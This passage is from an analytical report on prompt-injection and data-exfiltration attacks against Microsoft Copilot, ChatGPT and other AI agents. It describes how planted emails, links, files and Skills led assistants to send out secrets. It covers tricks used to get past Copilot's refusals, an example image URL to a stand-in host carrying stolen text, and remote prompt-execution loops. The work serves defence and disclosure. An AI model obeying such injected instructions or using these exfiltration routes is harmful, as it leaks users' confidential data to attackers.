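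On seven of the collections, triggers of five to ten tokens put the malicious item in the top five results almost every time. The paper's summary gives a success rate near 100 per cent across all 11, but the rate was lower on two harder collections, typically above 80 per cent and sometimes above 90, with triggers of around 15 tokens. The number of documents in a collection made no visible difference. The attack failed mostly where many genuine documents already matched the question closely, so a company with thorough documentation of its own has a little protection.

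Eight embedding models, old and new, were about equally vulnerable in a test on the financial questions. But a trigger built for one model often failed on another. One built on a small model from Alibaba's Qwen family worked 10 per cent of the time against OpenAI's, while triggers built on OpenAI's model averaged 74 per cent across the set. Chang and colleagues suspect that an attacker needs some knowledge of the target's embedding model, or a good guess. Aim Labs had the same difficulty with Copilot.

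Chang and colleagues also tested attacks from start to finish on AI agents that could search a mailbox. They used a mailbox from the Enron corpus, a public collection of real company email, and ten questions written by a language model that the mailbox's owner might ask. In the best-known result, a single email made a team of agents running GPT-4o, an older OpenAI model, send out the user's SSH keys, which are files that grant access to other computers, in 80 per cent of trials. When GPT-4o worked as a single agent, the same kind of attack succeeded 2 to 4 per cent of the time, although the email still reached the context. The researchers suggest that in the team, the agent that ran the code received only a script from another agent it trusted, not the email that led to it.

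In most of the mailbox tests, retrieval did not require the elaborate triggers. Copying the user's question in front of the instructions put the email in the top five every time, except in a test of a self-spreading email, where it worked for only 56 per cent of questions with GPT-4o. This helps to explain how EchoLeak could succeed when unprepared text in the BEIR collections was never retrieved. Aim Labs' headings were in effect guesses at the employee's questions, while the text planted in the BEIR collections was just a command to answer "Yes", unrelated to anything people were asking about.

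Chang and colleagues tried three defences at the retrieval stage. Rewording the user's question before the search reduced retrieval of the malicious text by less than 10 percentage points on most collections, and even that reduction disappeared when the attacker prepared for several wordings at once. A filter for unnatural text caught the triggers until the researchers repeated the malicious text and made it score as more natural than the genuine documents. Blanking out random tokens barely helped, because a few surviving trigger tokens were often enough to get the text retrieved.

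None of these rates applies directly to Copilot. The experiments used only vector search, and the researchers acknowledge that they did not test systems that combine it with keyword search or rerank the results. Copilot's search uses keywords and other signals besides vectors, so a string of odd tokens would probably do worse there. An email with sensible headings matches on keywords as well as meaning, so keyword search might even raise its ranking.

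### Links that carry a prompt

A web address can include information for the page it opens. The part after the question mark holds named values, called parameters, and search engines have long used one called "q" for the user's search terms. AI products adopted the same convention. In an example from *Reprompt* (Taler, 2026), a Copilot address had "Hello" in this parameter, and Copilot answered as if the user had typed the word and pressed Enter. The feature saves typing and lets other websites and scripts open the assistant with a question. Microsoft lists addresses of this form for Copilot, ChatGPT, Claude, Perplexity and Grok.

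An attacker can also use the feature by writing the prompt and sending the link to someone else. Varonis, the data-security company where Taler works, calls this parameter-to-prompt injection. Tenable had earlier described the behaviour in ChatGPT, and LayerX in Perplexity. The attack resembles cross-site request forgery, in which a link makes a logged-in person's browser carry out an action they did not choose.

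Anyone who can get a link in front of the victim, through email, a chat message or a web page, can try this attack. The victim must be logged in and click once. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026), which describes a since-patched attack on the search page of Microsoft 365 Copilot, says the victim sees Copilot appear to work for a moment and may get an odd answer, but by then the data has already been stolen.

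Once the victim clicks, the prompt always reaches the model, so the calculations about chunks and similarity no longer apply. The product itself enters the attacker's text as the user's request, so a defence that marks emails and documents as untrusted does not mark it. Because the request can tell Copilot to search, the attacker is not limited to whatever the victim was already asking about.

Phishing filters are poorly suited to catching such links because they look mainly for addresses with a bad reputation and for pages that imitate a login screen or deliver harmful software. The SearchLeak link used a Microsoft address and opened the real Copilot, which Varonis says is why conventional link protection let it through. Staff training also fails here, because employees learn to check that a link leads to the genuine site, as the SearchLeak link did.

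A filter could read the link's parameter as well as its domain. It would then have to decide whether ordinary language was a malicious instruction, which Microsoft's classifier failed to do in EchoLeak. Blocking every link that contains a prompt would be simpler, but would also break legitimate links.

Such links are already common in marketing. Over 60 days, Microsoft found 50 different prompts from 31 companies in web addresses sent through email. Many were behind buttons labelled "Summarize with AI", and they asked for a summary but also told the assistant to remember the company as a trusted source. All the senders were real businesses, including a security vendor, and free software for making the buttons was available online. Microsoft counted attempts but gives no success rate, and it could no longer reproduce several behaviours reported earlier. None of the 50 prompts tried to steal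 data, but they show that a button can hide a second instruction behind a useful one.

Taler advises vendors to treat text from a link as untrusted input, and advises users to read a pre-filled prompt before running it. Users can do that only if the prompt doesn't run automatically. If the assistant filled in the box and left the user to press Enter, the feature would keep most of its convenience and the victim would have a chance to see the attacker's text. A hurried reader might still miss the attack in a long prompt that opened with a harmless request for a summary.

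## How data leaves through displayed links, images and diagrams

A web address can carry a prompt into an assistant and stolen text out of it. As in EchoLeak, the text leaves when the victim's browser requests the address to follow a link or load an image.

### What the attacker's server records

Suppose the company in the merger calls the deal Heron and plans to offer 42 million. An assistant that followed a planted email might end its answer with an image at this invented address (nobody can register a domain ending in ".example"):

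`pictures.example/dot.png?note=Heron-offer-42m`

The browser asks pictures.example for the file, and the server there adds a line like this to its log:

`203.0.113.7 [14/May/2026:09:14:32] "GET /dot.png?note=Heron-offer-42m" 404`

The line records the requesting network address, the time and the request itself. The number 404 means that the server had no such picture, which makes no difference to the attacker. Checkmarx demonstrated an image leak in Microsoft's Copilot Chat, running in a development environment, in which no picture appeared in the chat but the request still delivered a secret key. Microsoft declined to class the leak as a vulnerability, partly because the attack needed several non-default steps and did not work reliably.

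Web addresses can't contain spaces or certain punctuation marks, so the planted instructions usually tell the model to encode the secret. The encoding affects how long the address is and what a person or a filter would detect in it.

| Encoding | How "Heron 42" looks in the address | Characters sent |
|---|---|---|
| Underscores for spaces | Heron_42 | 8 |
| Base64 (letters, digits and a few symbols) | SGVyb24gNDI= | 12 |
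| Hexadecimal (two digits per character) | 4865726f6e203432 | 16 |
| Invisible characters | Nothing visible | 96 |

A company that searched its outgoing traffic for the word "Heron" would catch only the top row.

Vendors mostly try to block these leaks by stripping links and images from the model's answer, escaping any HTML in it so that the browser shows an image's code instead of loading the image, and setting a content security policy. Researchers have bypassed all three defences in Copilot.

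### Invisible text in a link

A link sends data only when the user clicks it, so it has to look harmless. Rehberger's attack on Copilot in early 2024 hid the data in the link as invisible characters. Unicode, the standard that gives every written character a number, includes a set of "tag" characters that mirror ordinary letters, digits and punctuation. For example, the letter h has the hexadecimal number 68, and its tag counterpart has E0068. Most web applications don't display tag characters, so a link that ends in a hundred of them looks short and ordinary. When the user clicks it, the browser sends each one as a code of twelve visible characters, and the attacker converts the codes back into text.

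According to Embrace The Red, the planted email contained instructions for Copilot to hide another message's text in such a link, with a worked example to help the model encode it correctly. In the demonstrations, Copilot leaked sales figures and Slack login codes.

Rehberger first reported only the invisible characters, in January 2024, and Microsoft closed the report the next day as low severity. That was defensible, because the characters can't steal data by themselves. In February, Rehberger submitted the whole attack chain, and Microsoft opened a case three days later. By July the attack had stopped working, and Copilot seemed to have stopped displaying links.

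Rehberger had advised Microsoft not to display the hidden characters, preferably not to display links either, and not to let Copilot run searches without the user's approval. Microsoft did not reply when asked which of these it had done. Six months later, Aim Labs found that reference-style links still appeared in Copilot's answers, so Microsoft had probably added a filter, although from outside it had looked as if it had removed the ability to show links.

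### A login button drawn as a diagram

A filter on an answer's text can also miss links that another part of the program creates. Copilot can draw diagrams with Mermaid, a tool that turns text into flowcharts. A box in one of these diagrams can contain a link. In October 2025, the security researcher Adam Logue published an attack that used such a box to steal emails. BeyondMachines' *Microsoft 365 Copilot vulnerability enables data theft through malicious Mermaid diagrams* (2025) describes the steps.

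The attack began with an Excel workbook. Its first sheet held plausible financial figures and, in white text, an instruction to look at the second sheet before summarising anything. More white text on the second sheet changed the task in stages, until Copilot stopped summarising and told the user that the document was sensitive and required a login. According to Cyber Security News' *Copilot Prompt Injection Vulnerability*, Logue got the idea for these gradual changes from Microsoft's research on TaskTracker, a method for detecting when a model drifts from its assigned task.

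Meanwhile, Copilot used its email search tool to fetch the user's recent messages, listed their contents and converted the list to hexadecimal. Mermaid allows at most 200 characters per line, so the hidden text included an instruction to break the digits into lines of at most 30. Copilot then drew a diagram styled as a login button with a padlock and put the digits in the button's link address.

When a user clicked the button, it sent the emails to Logue's server. The server replied with a picture of Microsoft's real login screen, which appeared in a small window in place of the button. After a few seconds the window disappeared from the chat, leaving the user little evidence to show a security team.

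Like the early version of EchoLeak, this attack needed one click, but it gave the user a much stronger reason to click. A link at the end of a complete answer is easy to ignore, whereas users seemed to need Logue's button to see the summary they had asked for, and office workers are used to logging in.

Logue reported the full chain on 15 August 2025. Microsoft had trouble reproducing it at first, confirmed it on 8 September and fixed it by 26 September. The fix removed clickable links from Mermaid diagrams. BeyondMachines doubts that this covers every version of the attack, but gives no example of one that still works.

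Mermaid diagrams had already created a security flaw in Cursor, an AI code editor. Embrace The Red's *Cursor IDE* shows that a diagram could load an image from any server, which let data leave without a click. The user saw the diagram appear but could not watch the long address being written. Cursor released a fix in July 2025. A second record, CVELogic's *CVE-2025-61589*, covers versions up to 1.6 and mentions bypasses that the initial fix missed.

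### Escaping, and what else a web page can load

HTML, the language of web pages, uses angle brackets to mark instructions to the browser, such as one to load an image. Escaping replaces each bracket with a code that displays as a bracket, so the browser shows the instruction as text instead of carrying it out. Escaping is reliable when a program applies it to all text before the browser receives it.

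A product that is supposed to display HTML can't escape everything. In September or October 2025, Rehberger noticed that Copilot could show a working preview of a web page inside the chat. Microsoft had removed image tags from these previews, but a page can load other things from outside servers, and each request can carry data.

Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* explains that Rehberger found the gaps by asking Copilot. It wrote a page with as many ways to load an outside resource as it could generate, and a background image set in the page's style sheet worked. With more help from Copilot, he found that a style sheet could also request a font, which worked in more of the programs that include Copilot.

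The preview was hidden by default, and the user had to switch to it from the code view. When Rehberger added a few words to the planted text asking for the preview, Copilot opened it without a click. In one demonstration, the victim opened a shared Word document and typed "hi there" to Copilot. Copilot searched for an email with the subject "The Code" and sent its contents to Rehberger's server in the address of a font. Rehberger reported the flaw, CVE-2026-24299, on 16 October 2025, and Microsoft finished fixing it on 5 March 2026.

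### When an allowed site fetches other addresses

A content security policy was supposed to stop such requests in the browser. It has separate lists of allowed sources for images, fonts and other kinds of content. Copilot's font list was looser than its image list and allowed the font request to a server unrelated to Microsoft.

The lists also differed between the programs that Copilot appeared in, so the same answer could be safe in one and leak data in another. The image list included addresses under azureedge.net, a Microsoft service where customers can host their own content. It also included test systems, and some entries contained what looked like the user names of individual employees. Rehberger concluded that a content security policy is not a reliable security boundary in Copilot. The evidence supports that conclusion for Microsoft's lists, which had evidently grown without much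 control. It is weaker evidence against content security policies in general, since one with a few well-chosen entries would have blocked both the background image and the font.

Even a short list of allowed sites fails if one of them fetches other URLs, as Teams did in EchoLeak. The policy restricts the browser's requests but not the requests an allowed site's server then makes. The attacker's log looks the same as before, except that it shows the allowed site's network address.

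Relaying stolen data through an allowed site is an unusual use of server-side request forgery. Attackers typically use the technique to reach machines inside a private network, which may accept requests from the server that they would refuse from an outsider. A common defence is therefore to block requests to internal addresses. This doesn't prevent data theft through a relay, because the attacker's server is on the public internet and the service is meant to fetch content from there.

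Link previews, translation tools, image search and many other services fetch outside addresses by design. They may be safe until somebody adds their domain to the policy of a page that displays a model's answers. A policy entry that covers every address under a large domain also allows any such service that the domain's owner launches later, and the team that wrote the policy may never hear of it.

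### SearchLeak

SearchLeak, which Varonis published in June 2026, combined a relay with an escaping flaw. It targeted the search page of Microsoft 365 Copilot, where employees look for company emails, meetings and files. Varonis had already used prompts in links against the consumer version of Copilot, and its researchers were surprised that the method still worked against the business version.

Once the victim clicked the link, the prompt inside it told Copilot to find an email, replace the spaces in its title with underscores and write an HTML image tag with that title in the image's address.

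Microsoft's safeguard put the model's output in a code block so that the browser would treat any HTML as text. But Copilot streams its answers, displaying them while the model is still writing, and the safeguard ran only when the answer was complete. Until then, the page contained raw HTML. Varonis found that the browser loaded the image as soon as its tag appeared, so the request was sent before the code block was applied. This is a race condition, meaning that the result depends on which of two events happens first.

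The page's content security policy would have blocked an image from the attacker's server, but it allowed every address under bing.com. Bing's "Search by Image" feature takes the address of a picture and fetches the picture to analyse it. The attacker used a Bing address that contained the address of their own server, with the stolen title included. The victim's browser contacted Bing, Bing's server contacted the attacker's, and the title appeared in the attacker's log.

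The sample log line Varonis published contains a request for an image in a folder named "Your_Security_Code_847291". An email's subject line can be worth stealing because many services put one-time login codes in it. According to The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox*, such codes often remain valid for several minutes. An attacker who already had the victim's password for another service could try to log in there, wait for the service to send the code and use SearchLeak to collect it.

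Varonis also lists salary records, acquisition plans and meeting notes among the data at risk, although the published demonstration took only a title.

Microsoft fixed SearchLeak on its own servers. Its advisory, *CVE-2026-42824*, rates the flaw critical and records no exploitation, although published accounts give it different CVSS scores.

Varonis seems to overstate its case when it says that each of the three weaknesses was necessary, and that without the prompt in the link an attacker could not have got HTML into the answer. EchoLeak had already shown that a planted email can also dictate what Copilot writes, so a vendor that repaired only the link would leave the other two weaknesses for the next attacker to use. One of the ReLeak chains, which started with an email, later used Bing as a relay too.

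### Why old web flaws matter more here

Web programmers have known for well over a decade about race conditions in filters and about servers that fetch any address they are given. Many of these flaws were of little use to attackers. Anyone could ask Bing to fetch a picture from their own server, but they would learn nothing because they had no secret to put in the address. An attack needed someone or something that could read the victim's mail, such as a copilot, to write the address.

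On an ordinary website, an attacker would usually have to run code in the victim's browser to do that. Browser makers and website owners have spent years making this harder, and content security policies were invented largely for that purpose. A copilot gives the attacker another way, because it can already read the mail and it writes text that the browser will display. A sentence in plain English may be enough to make it put the mail into that text. Rehberger's invisible characters went from "low severity" to a serious flaw within a month because he showed that Copilot could be told to fill them with someone's email.

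Security teams therefore can't judge a small flaw by what it allowed before the copilot was added. Varonis advises them to review every allowed domain for services that fetch addresses users supply, and to clean a model's output as it is displayed, not afterwards.

### Removing a feature or filtering its output

Microsoft responded to the Mermaid attack by removing clickable links from diagrams. Unlike most of its other defences, this left attackers no filter to fool, because there were no links to inspect. Users lost little, because they can read a flowchart without clicking on it.

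In the other cases, Microsoft kept the feature and filtered the output, so the filter had to recognise every way the output could trigger a network request. It missed a second notation for links in EchoLeak, style sheets and fonts in the HTML preview, and everything that appeared on screen before the filter ran in SearchLeak.

Microsoft distinguishes probabilistic defences, which make an attack less likely to succeed, from deterministic ones, which guarantee that a particular attack will fail. It classes its blocks on Markdown images and "certain untrusted links" as deterministic. The distinction is sound, but the guarantee covers only the routes the block's designers anticipated. A rule that misses reference-style links will miss them every time, so an attacker can exploit it more reliably than a classifier that sometimes catches them.

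Removal can also fail, because a new feature can reopen the route. Rehberger noticed the HTML preview at about the time Microsoft was removing links from diagrams. A vendor would have to apply the same rule to everything that can display an answer, including features another team hasn't built yet.

Some features, such as links to an assistant's sources, are also too useful to remove. Google closed Checkmarx's report about links in Gemini after four days as infeasible to fix. Google removes links that its Safe Browsing service lists as malicious, but an attacker can register a new domain that isn't listed yet.

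Rehberger recommends a compromise that Google and OpenAI already use and that Copilot apparently lacked in spring 2026. The assistant loads an address automatically only if a search engine has already indexed it as a public page. An address that the model has just made up to carry a secret will not be indexed. This prevents large thefts, but small ones remain possible. An attacker could publish ten ordinary pages, one for each digit, wait for the search engine to index them and then have the assistant load them in the order of the digits in a login code.

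## How data leaves through files, code and network requests

If Copilot displayed its answers as plain text, with no links, images or diagrams, attackers could no longer use the routes that EchoLeak and SearchLeak used to get data out. That might be enough for an assistant that can only write answers, but Copilot can also create files and run code, and other assistants can browse the web or send email. Each of these abilities adds a route for data to leave the system, which security engineers call "egress", that a filter on the displayed answer doesn't cover.

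*Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* distinguishes chat-only assistants, which normally disclose information only through the text they write, from assistants with tools, which can also choose an outside destination and send information there. With a tool-using assistant, an attacker could steal the terms of the merger without needing the finance director's browser to load a picture.

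Some of these abilities have their own checks. For example, Microsoft requires the user's approval before Copilot sends an email. But no one approves the requests a server makes while processing a file.

### ReLeak: one way in, three ways out

On 3 December 2026, Simonovich published the three ReLeak attacks for Cato AI Labs, formerly Aim Labs. Like EchoLeak, all three began with an unread email that Copilot retrieved when an employee asked an ordinary work question. In *Письмо даже не нужно открывать* ("You don't even need to open the email"), Antipov (2026) adds that the employee didn't have to approve extra permissions.

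The attacks differed in how the data got out. One, CVE-2026-124115, put the data in an image address that Bing fetched, as SearchLeak had, but didn't require the victim to click a link first. Microsoft had already fixed SearchLeak when Varonis published it in June 2026, so the fix had evidently left some route through Bing open. Microsoft closed the route that Cato found in mid-November.

The other two exits did not involve the displayed answer at all.

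### A file that leaks without anyone opening it

In CVE-2026-124132, the planted email made Copilot save a Word, Excel, PowerPoint or PDF file containing a link with the confidential text in its address. Microsoft's servers then processed the file in the background and contacted that address, which delivered the text to the attacker. According to Antipov, this happened in Cato's tests one to eight minutes after the conversation with Copilot ended, even if the employee never opened the file.

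Cloud storage services routinely open new files automatically, for example to create a preview, index the text or scan for viruses. Antipov places the flaw in the background processing of OneDrive and SharePoint files, but doesn't identify the process that made the request. Since nobody had to click the link, the software must have either followed it automatically or loaded the address as it would a picture stored on another site.

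None of the chat window's defences stops data from leaving this way. Copilot's written answer could be harmless, so a filter would have nothing to remove. The content security policy had no effect either, because the browser loaded nothing. The delay also makes the theft harder to trace, because an investigator would have to connect a request from a Microsoft server to a chat that ended several minutes earlier.

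Microsoft has patched the flaw. The most reliable fix would be to block background processes from contacting outside addresses, since no program would then need to identify suspicious links. The drawback would be small, as previews would only lose pictures that documents legitimately include from other sites.

### A sandbox without a network

Language models are unreliable at calculation, so Copilot writes a short Python program when it has to analyse a spreadsheet or build a chart. It runs the program in a sandbox, an isolated environment that limits what the code can reach. An outsider's email can influence the code Copilot writes, so an internet connection in the sandbox would give an attacker an obvious way to send data out. Antipov reports that Microsoft guarantees in its documentation that no network traffic enters or leaves these sandboxes.

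In *Breaking the M365 Copilot Sandbox with ChatMate*, Lahav (2026) examined this isolation from inside the sandbox. It had no internet connection, and DNS, which turns site names into network addresses, was deliberately disabled. Web traffic settings pointed to a local relay that refused every request, and the sandboxes of other Copilot sessions were out of reach. Copilot also declined to run code that seemed to inspect its surroundings, but Lahav got past this by disguising the code's purpose.

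Still, a sandbox like this can't be sealed completely, because at least one program inside has to receive code from Copilot and return the results. Lahav also found a service that the sandbox could reach but that ran on the host, the machine underneath, with full administrative rights. A flaw in that service, CVE-2026-32193 (CVSS score 8.8), let code in the sandbox create files on the host. Lahav eventually used it to escape the sandbox completely and reach the victim's Microsoft 365 data, starting from a malicious document.

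The vulnerable service was part of infrastructure that several Microsoft cloud products share, so the designers of Copilot's sandbox may have had little reason to examine it.

Cato's researchers also got data out of the sandbox. In CVE-2026-78501, the planted email made Copilot run Python code that bypassed the network restrictions and sent confidential data straight to an outside server. Faisal and Antipov don't explain how the bypass worked. The flaw has its own CVE number, so it appears to be different from Lahav's, but the two could still have something in common. CVE-2026-78501 has a CVSS score of 8.6, raised from an initial 7.4. Agents that customers build with Microsoft's Agent Builder and Copilot Studio can use the same code interpreter, though nobody has confirmed that the flaw affected them.

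Network isolation is still a worthwhile defence despite these escapes, because it doesn't depend on recognising malicious text and seems to have been hard to defeat. Lahav gained full control inside the sandbox and found the flaw in the host's service, but could not turn either into a useful attack and set the work aside for about a month.

That kind of persistence may be getting easier, because attackers could use AI agents as Cato did to look for weaknesses in Copilot. Under the researchers' direction, the agents wrote test cases, analysed Copilot's refusals and adjusted the next attempts.

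Even a perfectly isolated sandbox would probably not have stopped the leak through generated files. According to Lahav, the model makes a PDF by writing Python code that creates the file in the sandbox. The user is supposed to receive that file, so a secret inside it leaves the sandbox by the intended route. A server with an internet connection can then open the file.

### How much had changed since EchoLeak

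Faisal quotes Cato's conclusion that "too little progress has been made" in the year since EchoLeak. Cato has a commercial interest here, but its evidence on how attackers get in is strong. An outsider's email could still direct Copilot, and Microsoft's defences against cross-prompt injection blocked none of the three attack chains.

The evidence doesn't show how often those defences work. Cato's agents kept revising their tests, and neither press account gives the number of failed attempts or a success rate for the finished attacks. A persistent attacker could evidently get through, but Microsoft's filters may still stop many cruder emails.

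The verdict is fair for the image exit, because Cato used a kind of relay that Varonis had already made public. The file and sandbox exits are a somewhat different problem, because they depend on work that Copilot does beyond writing an answer. Both would have remained even if Microsoft had fixed every flaw in how Copilot displays text. Cato knew of no customers who had lost data through any of the three exits.

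### Requests that start on the provider's servers

The security firm Radware had demonstrated a similar problem in ChatGPT in September 2025. Its attack, ShadowLeak, targeted Deep Research, a mode in which ChatGPT spends several minutes gathering material before writing a report. Users could connect Deep Research to their Gmail accounts.

The attacker sent the victim an email with instructions hidden in its formatting. When the victim asked Deep Research to go through recent messages, the agent also read the planted email. It then took personal details from another email, encoded them and opened a web address that contained them. OpenAI fixed the flaw before Radware published it.

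Deep Research runs on OpenAI's servers and opened the address from there, so the request went directly to the attacker without passing through the victim's computer or the employer's network. Even in a complete log of staff connections, the attack would have looked like normal use of ChatGPT.

The starting point of the request determines who has a chance of noticing it.

| Exit | What first sends the stolen data | What crosses the victim's own network |
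|---|---|---|
| ReLeak: image | The victim's browser | A request to Bing that contains the data |
| ReLeak: generated file | Microsoft's file-processing servers | No request containing the data in its address |
| ReLeak: Python code | Microsoft's sandbox | No request containing the data in its address |
| ShadowLeak | OpenAI's servers | No request containing the data in its address |

An employer might catch the image request, but it would be hard. Web traffic is normally encrypted, so the employer would need software on the employee's computer, or a company relay that decrypts traffic, to read the full address. It would then have to notice something odd about a request to Bing. With the other exits, the employer has no such request to inspect. Only the provider can block requests made through those exits, and its logs may be the only record of them outside the attacker's own.

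### Why a harmless answer proves little

Testers often judge an assistant by the text it produces. In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) also recorded network requests to measure how many leaks this approach would miss.

The researchers, who work at eBay, built a simple assistant that automatically previewed web pages and could make web requests. It used qwen2.5:7b, a small language model run on their own equipment. In every run, the user asked for a summary of a page. The model's context contained an invented secret, and the page contained an instruction to send that secret to a server the researchers controlled. The instruction described this as a routine technical check.

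The researchers put the instruction in the page's title, its body, the text of a link, or the description that a site supplies for previews. The assistant reached the page either directly or through a chain of redirects. In the instruction, the researchers requested the secret either whole or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times, for a total of 480 runs.

The assistant contacted the researchers' server in 423 runs, or 88 per cent. Based on their detailed figures, this works out at 238 of 240 runs when the instruction asked for the whole secret and 185 of 240 when it asked for pieces. The final answer gave no sign of a leak in 95 per cent of the successful attacks.

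The model makes a tool call, receives the result and continues, and it writes its answer to the user only after the theft is over. The attacker has no reason to spoil that answer, since a good summary makes the user less likely to suspect anything. A tester who reads only the summary could wrongly conclude that the assistant ignored the planted instruction.

Lan and colleagues also ran the assistant 120 times on harmless pages, and it never contacted their server. They take this as evidence that network requests are a very clear signal of an attack. That seems too strong, because the harmless pages didn't include the server's address, so the assistant had almost no way to contact it by accident. Malicious requests would be harder to pick out in an office, where assistants make many legitimate requests to many sites.

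Splitting the secret across several requests makes the theft even harder to detect. Many companies use data loss prevention software, which searches outgoing traffic for material such as passwords and customer records, but four characters from the middle of a key look like any other short code in a web address. When the assistant sent the secret in pieces, the share of runs in which sensitive data appeared in the first request fell from 97 to 26 per cent.

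The paper's figure for the first three requests is even lower, at 16 per cent. This can't be right under the paper's own definition, because anything in the first request is also among the first three. The paper also doesn't report how often all four pieces arrived, so in some of the 185 runs the attacker may have received only part of the secret.

The researchers then tested several defences against the version of the attack that put its instruction in the page's body and asked for the whole secret. Without any defence, the data leaked in all 30 runs. Marking the page's text as untrusted made no difference. A system instruction never to obey web content reduced the leaks to 20 of 30, and combining the two reduced them to 17. A list of approved domains stopped every leak. The model still tried to send the secret every time, but ordinary software checked the destination and blocked the request.

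In this test the attacker's domain was not on the list, but Lan and colleagues acknowledge that a real attacker could go through an approved site that forwards requests, as Cato did with Bing.

Their results for filters that inspect the contents of an address are harder to accept. A filter for words such as "password" reportedly prevented every leak, yet it triggered in only 23 per cent of runs. The researchers suggest that the model was disguising the secret in the other runs, but if so, it's unclear what stopped those requests.

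The 88 per cent figure is a poor guide to how often Copilot or ChatGPT would leak data. Lan and colleagues call their success rates a lower bound because they used simple instructions, but they also say they deliberately set up the test to favour the attacker. The model was small, the secret was already in its context, and the system instructions contained little beyond how to call the tool. They argue that larger models might be more vulnerable because they follow instructions better, but they did not test any. The one GPT-4o agent Chang and colleagues tested rarely leaked the user's keys.

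The reason to check network traffic depends much less on the model, because any assistant that can call tools can leak data and still write a harmless answer. Lan and colleagues could count every leak because they ran both the assistant and the receiving server. A company can run a similar test on a hosted assistant by planting an instruction and watching a server it controls, but the test would cover only the instructions and routes out that the company had thought to try.

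## How one injection becomes continuing control

The EchoLeak attacker had to write every instruction in advance and accept whatever the model sent back. In 2026, researchers published attacks on Microsoft's Copilot products in which the attacker, after one click or one uploaded file, could read the first stolen item, decide what to ask for next and get an answer.

An attacker can turn one injection into continuing control only if the assistant reads the reply to the request that carries the data out. When a browser loads an image, the attacker's server can send anything back, but the browser only tries to display it and the model never receives it. When the assistant opens a web page itself, the page becomes part of its context, so the attacker can receive data through the address and send back a new instruction in the page. Length limits on web addresses also matter less, because the attacker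 can spread the data over several requests.

### Reprompt: a chain of fetched instructions

Reprompt targeted Copilot Personal, the consumer version. The victim clicked a link containing a prompt that made Copilot open an address on the attacker's server. Taler had to get past two safeguards. Copilot usually refused to open an address without a good reason, so the prompt presented the request as a puzzle about identifying a bird. Copilot could also remove sensitive data from an address before opening it, but only on the first request, so the prompt told Copilot to do everything twice. In a test with an invented secret phrase, Copilot removed the phrase the first time and sent it the second time.

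Those two tricks alone would have leaked data only once. To keep the leak going, the attacker also used the prompt to tell Copilot to follow whatever instructions the server returned. In the first reply, the attacker asked for the user's local time and supplied a new address to put it in. In later replies, the attacker asked for the user's location, then for everything Copilot had learned about the user, then for a summary of the last conversation. Each answer reached the attacker inside the next address that Copilot opened.

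The attack continued after the victim closed the Copilot tab because the victim's session remained valid. Inspecting the link would not have revealed what the attacker wanted, because the server sent most of the questions later.

Copilot could reveal only information it already had or could look up for that user, so Taler overstates the risk in saying that there was no limit to the amount or type of data an attacker could take. Varonis could also have written the questions in the published chain beforehand. A server could choose its next question based on the last answer, for example after learning the victim's industry, but the published steps don't show this.

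Microsoft patched Reprompt in January 2026, according to TechRepublic's *How ‘Reprompt’ Attack Let Hackers Steal Data From Microsoft Copilot* (2026). Microsoft 365 Copilot, the version that companies buy, was not vulnerable.

### ChatMate: a person at the other end

ChatMate did affect Microsoft 365 Copilot, as the final stage of Lahav's escape from Copilot's Python sandbox. The machine underneath had an internet connection, unlike the sandbox, but Lahav could not reach other customers' sandboxes from it. For about a week, Lahav thought an attacker could steal only the documents that happened to pass through the victim's own sandbox.

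The attack became much more powerful once Lahav also used the connection to send messages to Copilot. Copilot reads the output of every program it runs, so a program that prints an attacker's message puts that message into Copilot's context.

Rubrik Zero Labs, the research group where Lahav works, describes the attack as starting with a Word document that looked like routine business. A white rectangle covered the malicious instructions. When the victim uploaded the document and asked Copilot to fill in the details, the hidden text made Copilot run the attacker's code without mentioning it. It also told Copilot to treat the program's output as instructions and to send the results back into the sandbox. This set up a loop:

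1. The attacker typed a prompt, which travelled over the internet to the machine underneath and from there into the sandbox.
2. The program in the sandbox returned the prompt to Copilot as its output.
3. Copilot carried out the prompt with the victim's access to mail, files, calendar and chats.
4. Copilot sent its answer back into the sandbox, and the attacker received it and typed the next prompt.

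In the merger example, an attacker could ask for the finance director's calendar, notice a meeting about Heron and then ask for the latest draft of the offer. The attacker would not have to guess the project's name in advance. The loop ended when the attacker stopped or when Copilot reached its maximum number of turns.

Microsoft had fixed the flaws by mid-April 2026, before Lahav recorded the demonstration, so the video simulates the internet connection to the attacker. Rubrik says everything else in it is real.

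Lahav calls this kind of attack remote prompt execution, by analogy with remote code execution, in which an attacker runs programs on someone else's computer. In remote prompt execution, an attacker can repeatedly send prompts to a victim's logged-in assistant, read the output and adapt the next prompt, with no further action by the victim. Rubrik presents ChatMate as the first documented case. Lahav acknowledges that Reprompt had a closely related control loop, but points out that its write-up did not show a person typing prompts and reading complete answers.

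Reprompt and ChatMate differ most in how they got their connection. Reprompt used Copilot's ordinary ability to open web pages, while ChatMate worked against an assistant whose code was supposed to have no connection. The presence of a human operator seems a weak basis for distinguishing them, since an attacker could have another language model choose the follow-up questions.

The attack was hard to build, and Lahav counts five separate flaws in Microsoft's cloud services found in the process. Reusing the finished attack might have been easy until Microsoft fixed those flaws. *Phantom Keystrokes* (Fiehler, 2026), Rubrik's account for business readers, describes the attack as "relatively easy to do".

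### Copilot Cowork: a program that takes orders

In ChatMate, every command went through the language model. PromptArmor's *Copilot Cowork Sandbox Bypass Gives Attackers Remote Control* describes an attack in which the model only had to start a program. Copilot Cowork is an agent in Microsoft 365 that finds and acts on data with the user's permissions. Users can extend it with Skills, packages of instructions that may include scripts and up to 20 companion files.

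In the demonstration, a user asked Cowork to use a Skill found online to check a contract against a proposal. One of the Skill's scripts produced a complete report on inconsistencies. It also bypassed the sandbox's network restrictions, collected commands from PromptArmor's server, ran them and sent back the results. PromptArmor used these commands to list the user's Outlook messages and open an email thread about a deal.

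A filter on prompts would have had little to inspect once the script was running, because the script could run commands without the model. The stop button ended the agent's turn but left background programs running. A user who noticed something odd and pressed it would reasonably have believed that the danger was over.

This attack required the user to add the Skill, which is closer to installing a stranger's software than to reading a stranger's email. But PromptArmor notes that a prompt injection could also have led Cowork to run code that used the same bypass, and colleagues can share Skills within a company.

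PromptArmor warns that one malicious Skill file can also affect many chats, because Cowork automatically loads Skill files from the user's OneDrive and decides when to use them. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* raises a similar concern about scheduled tasks, which run repeatedly without anyone watching. Microsoft had mitigated the sandbox bypass by 19 August 2026, eight weeks after PromptArmor reported it. Users who had added a malicious Skill would still need to remove its files from OneDrive.

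### CoSnitch, and which Copilot it affected

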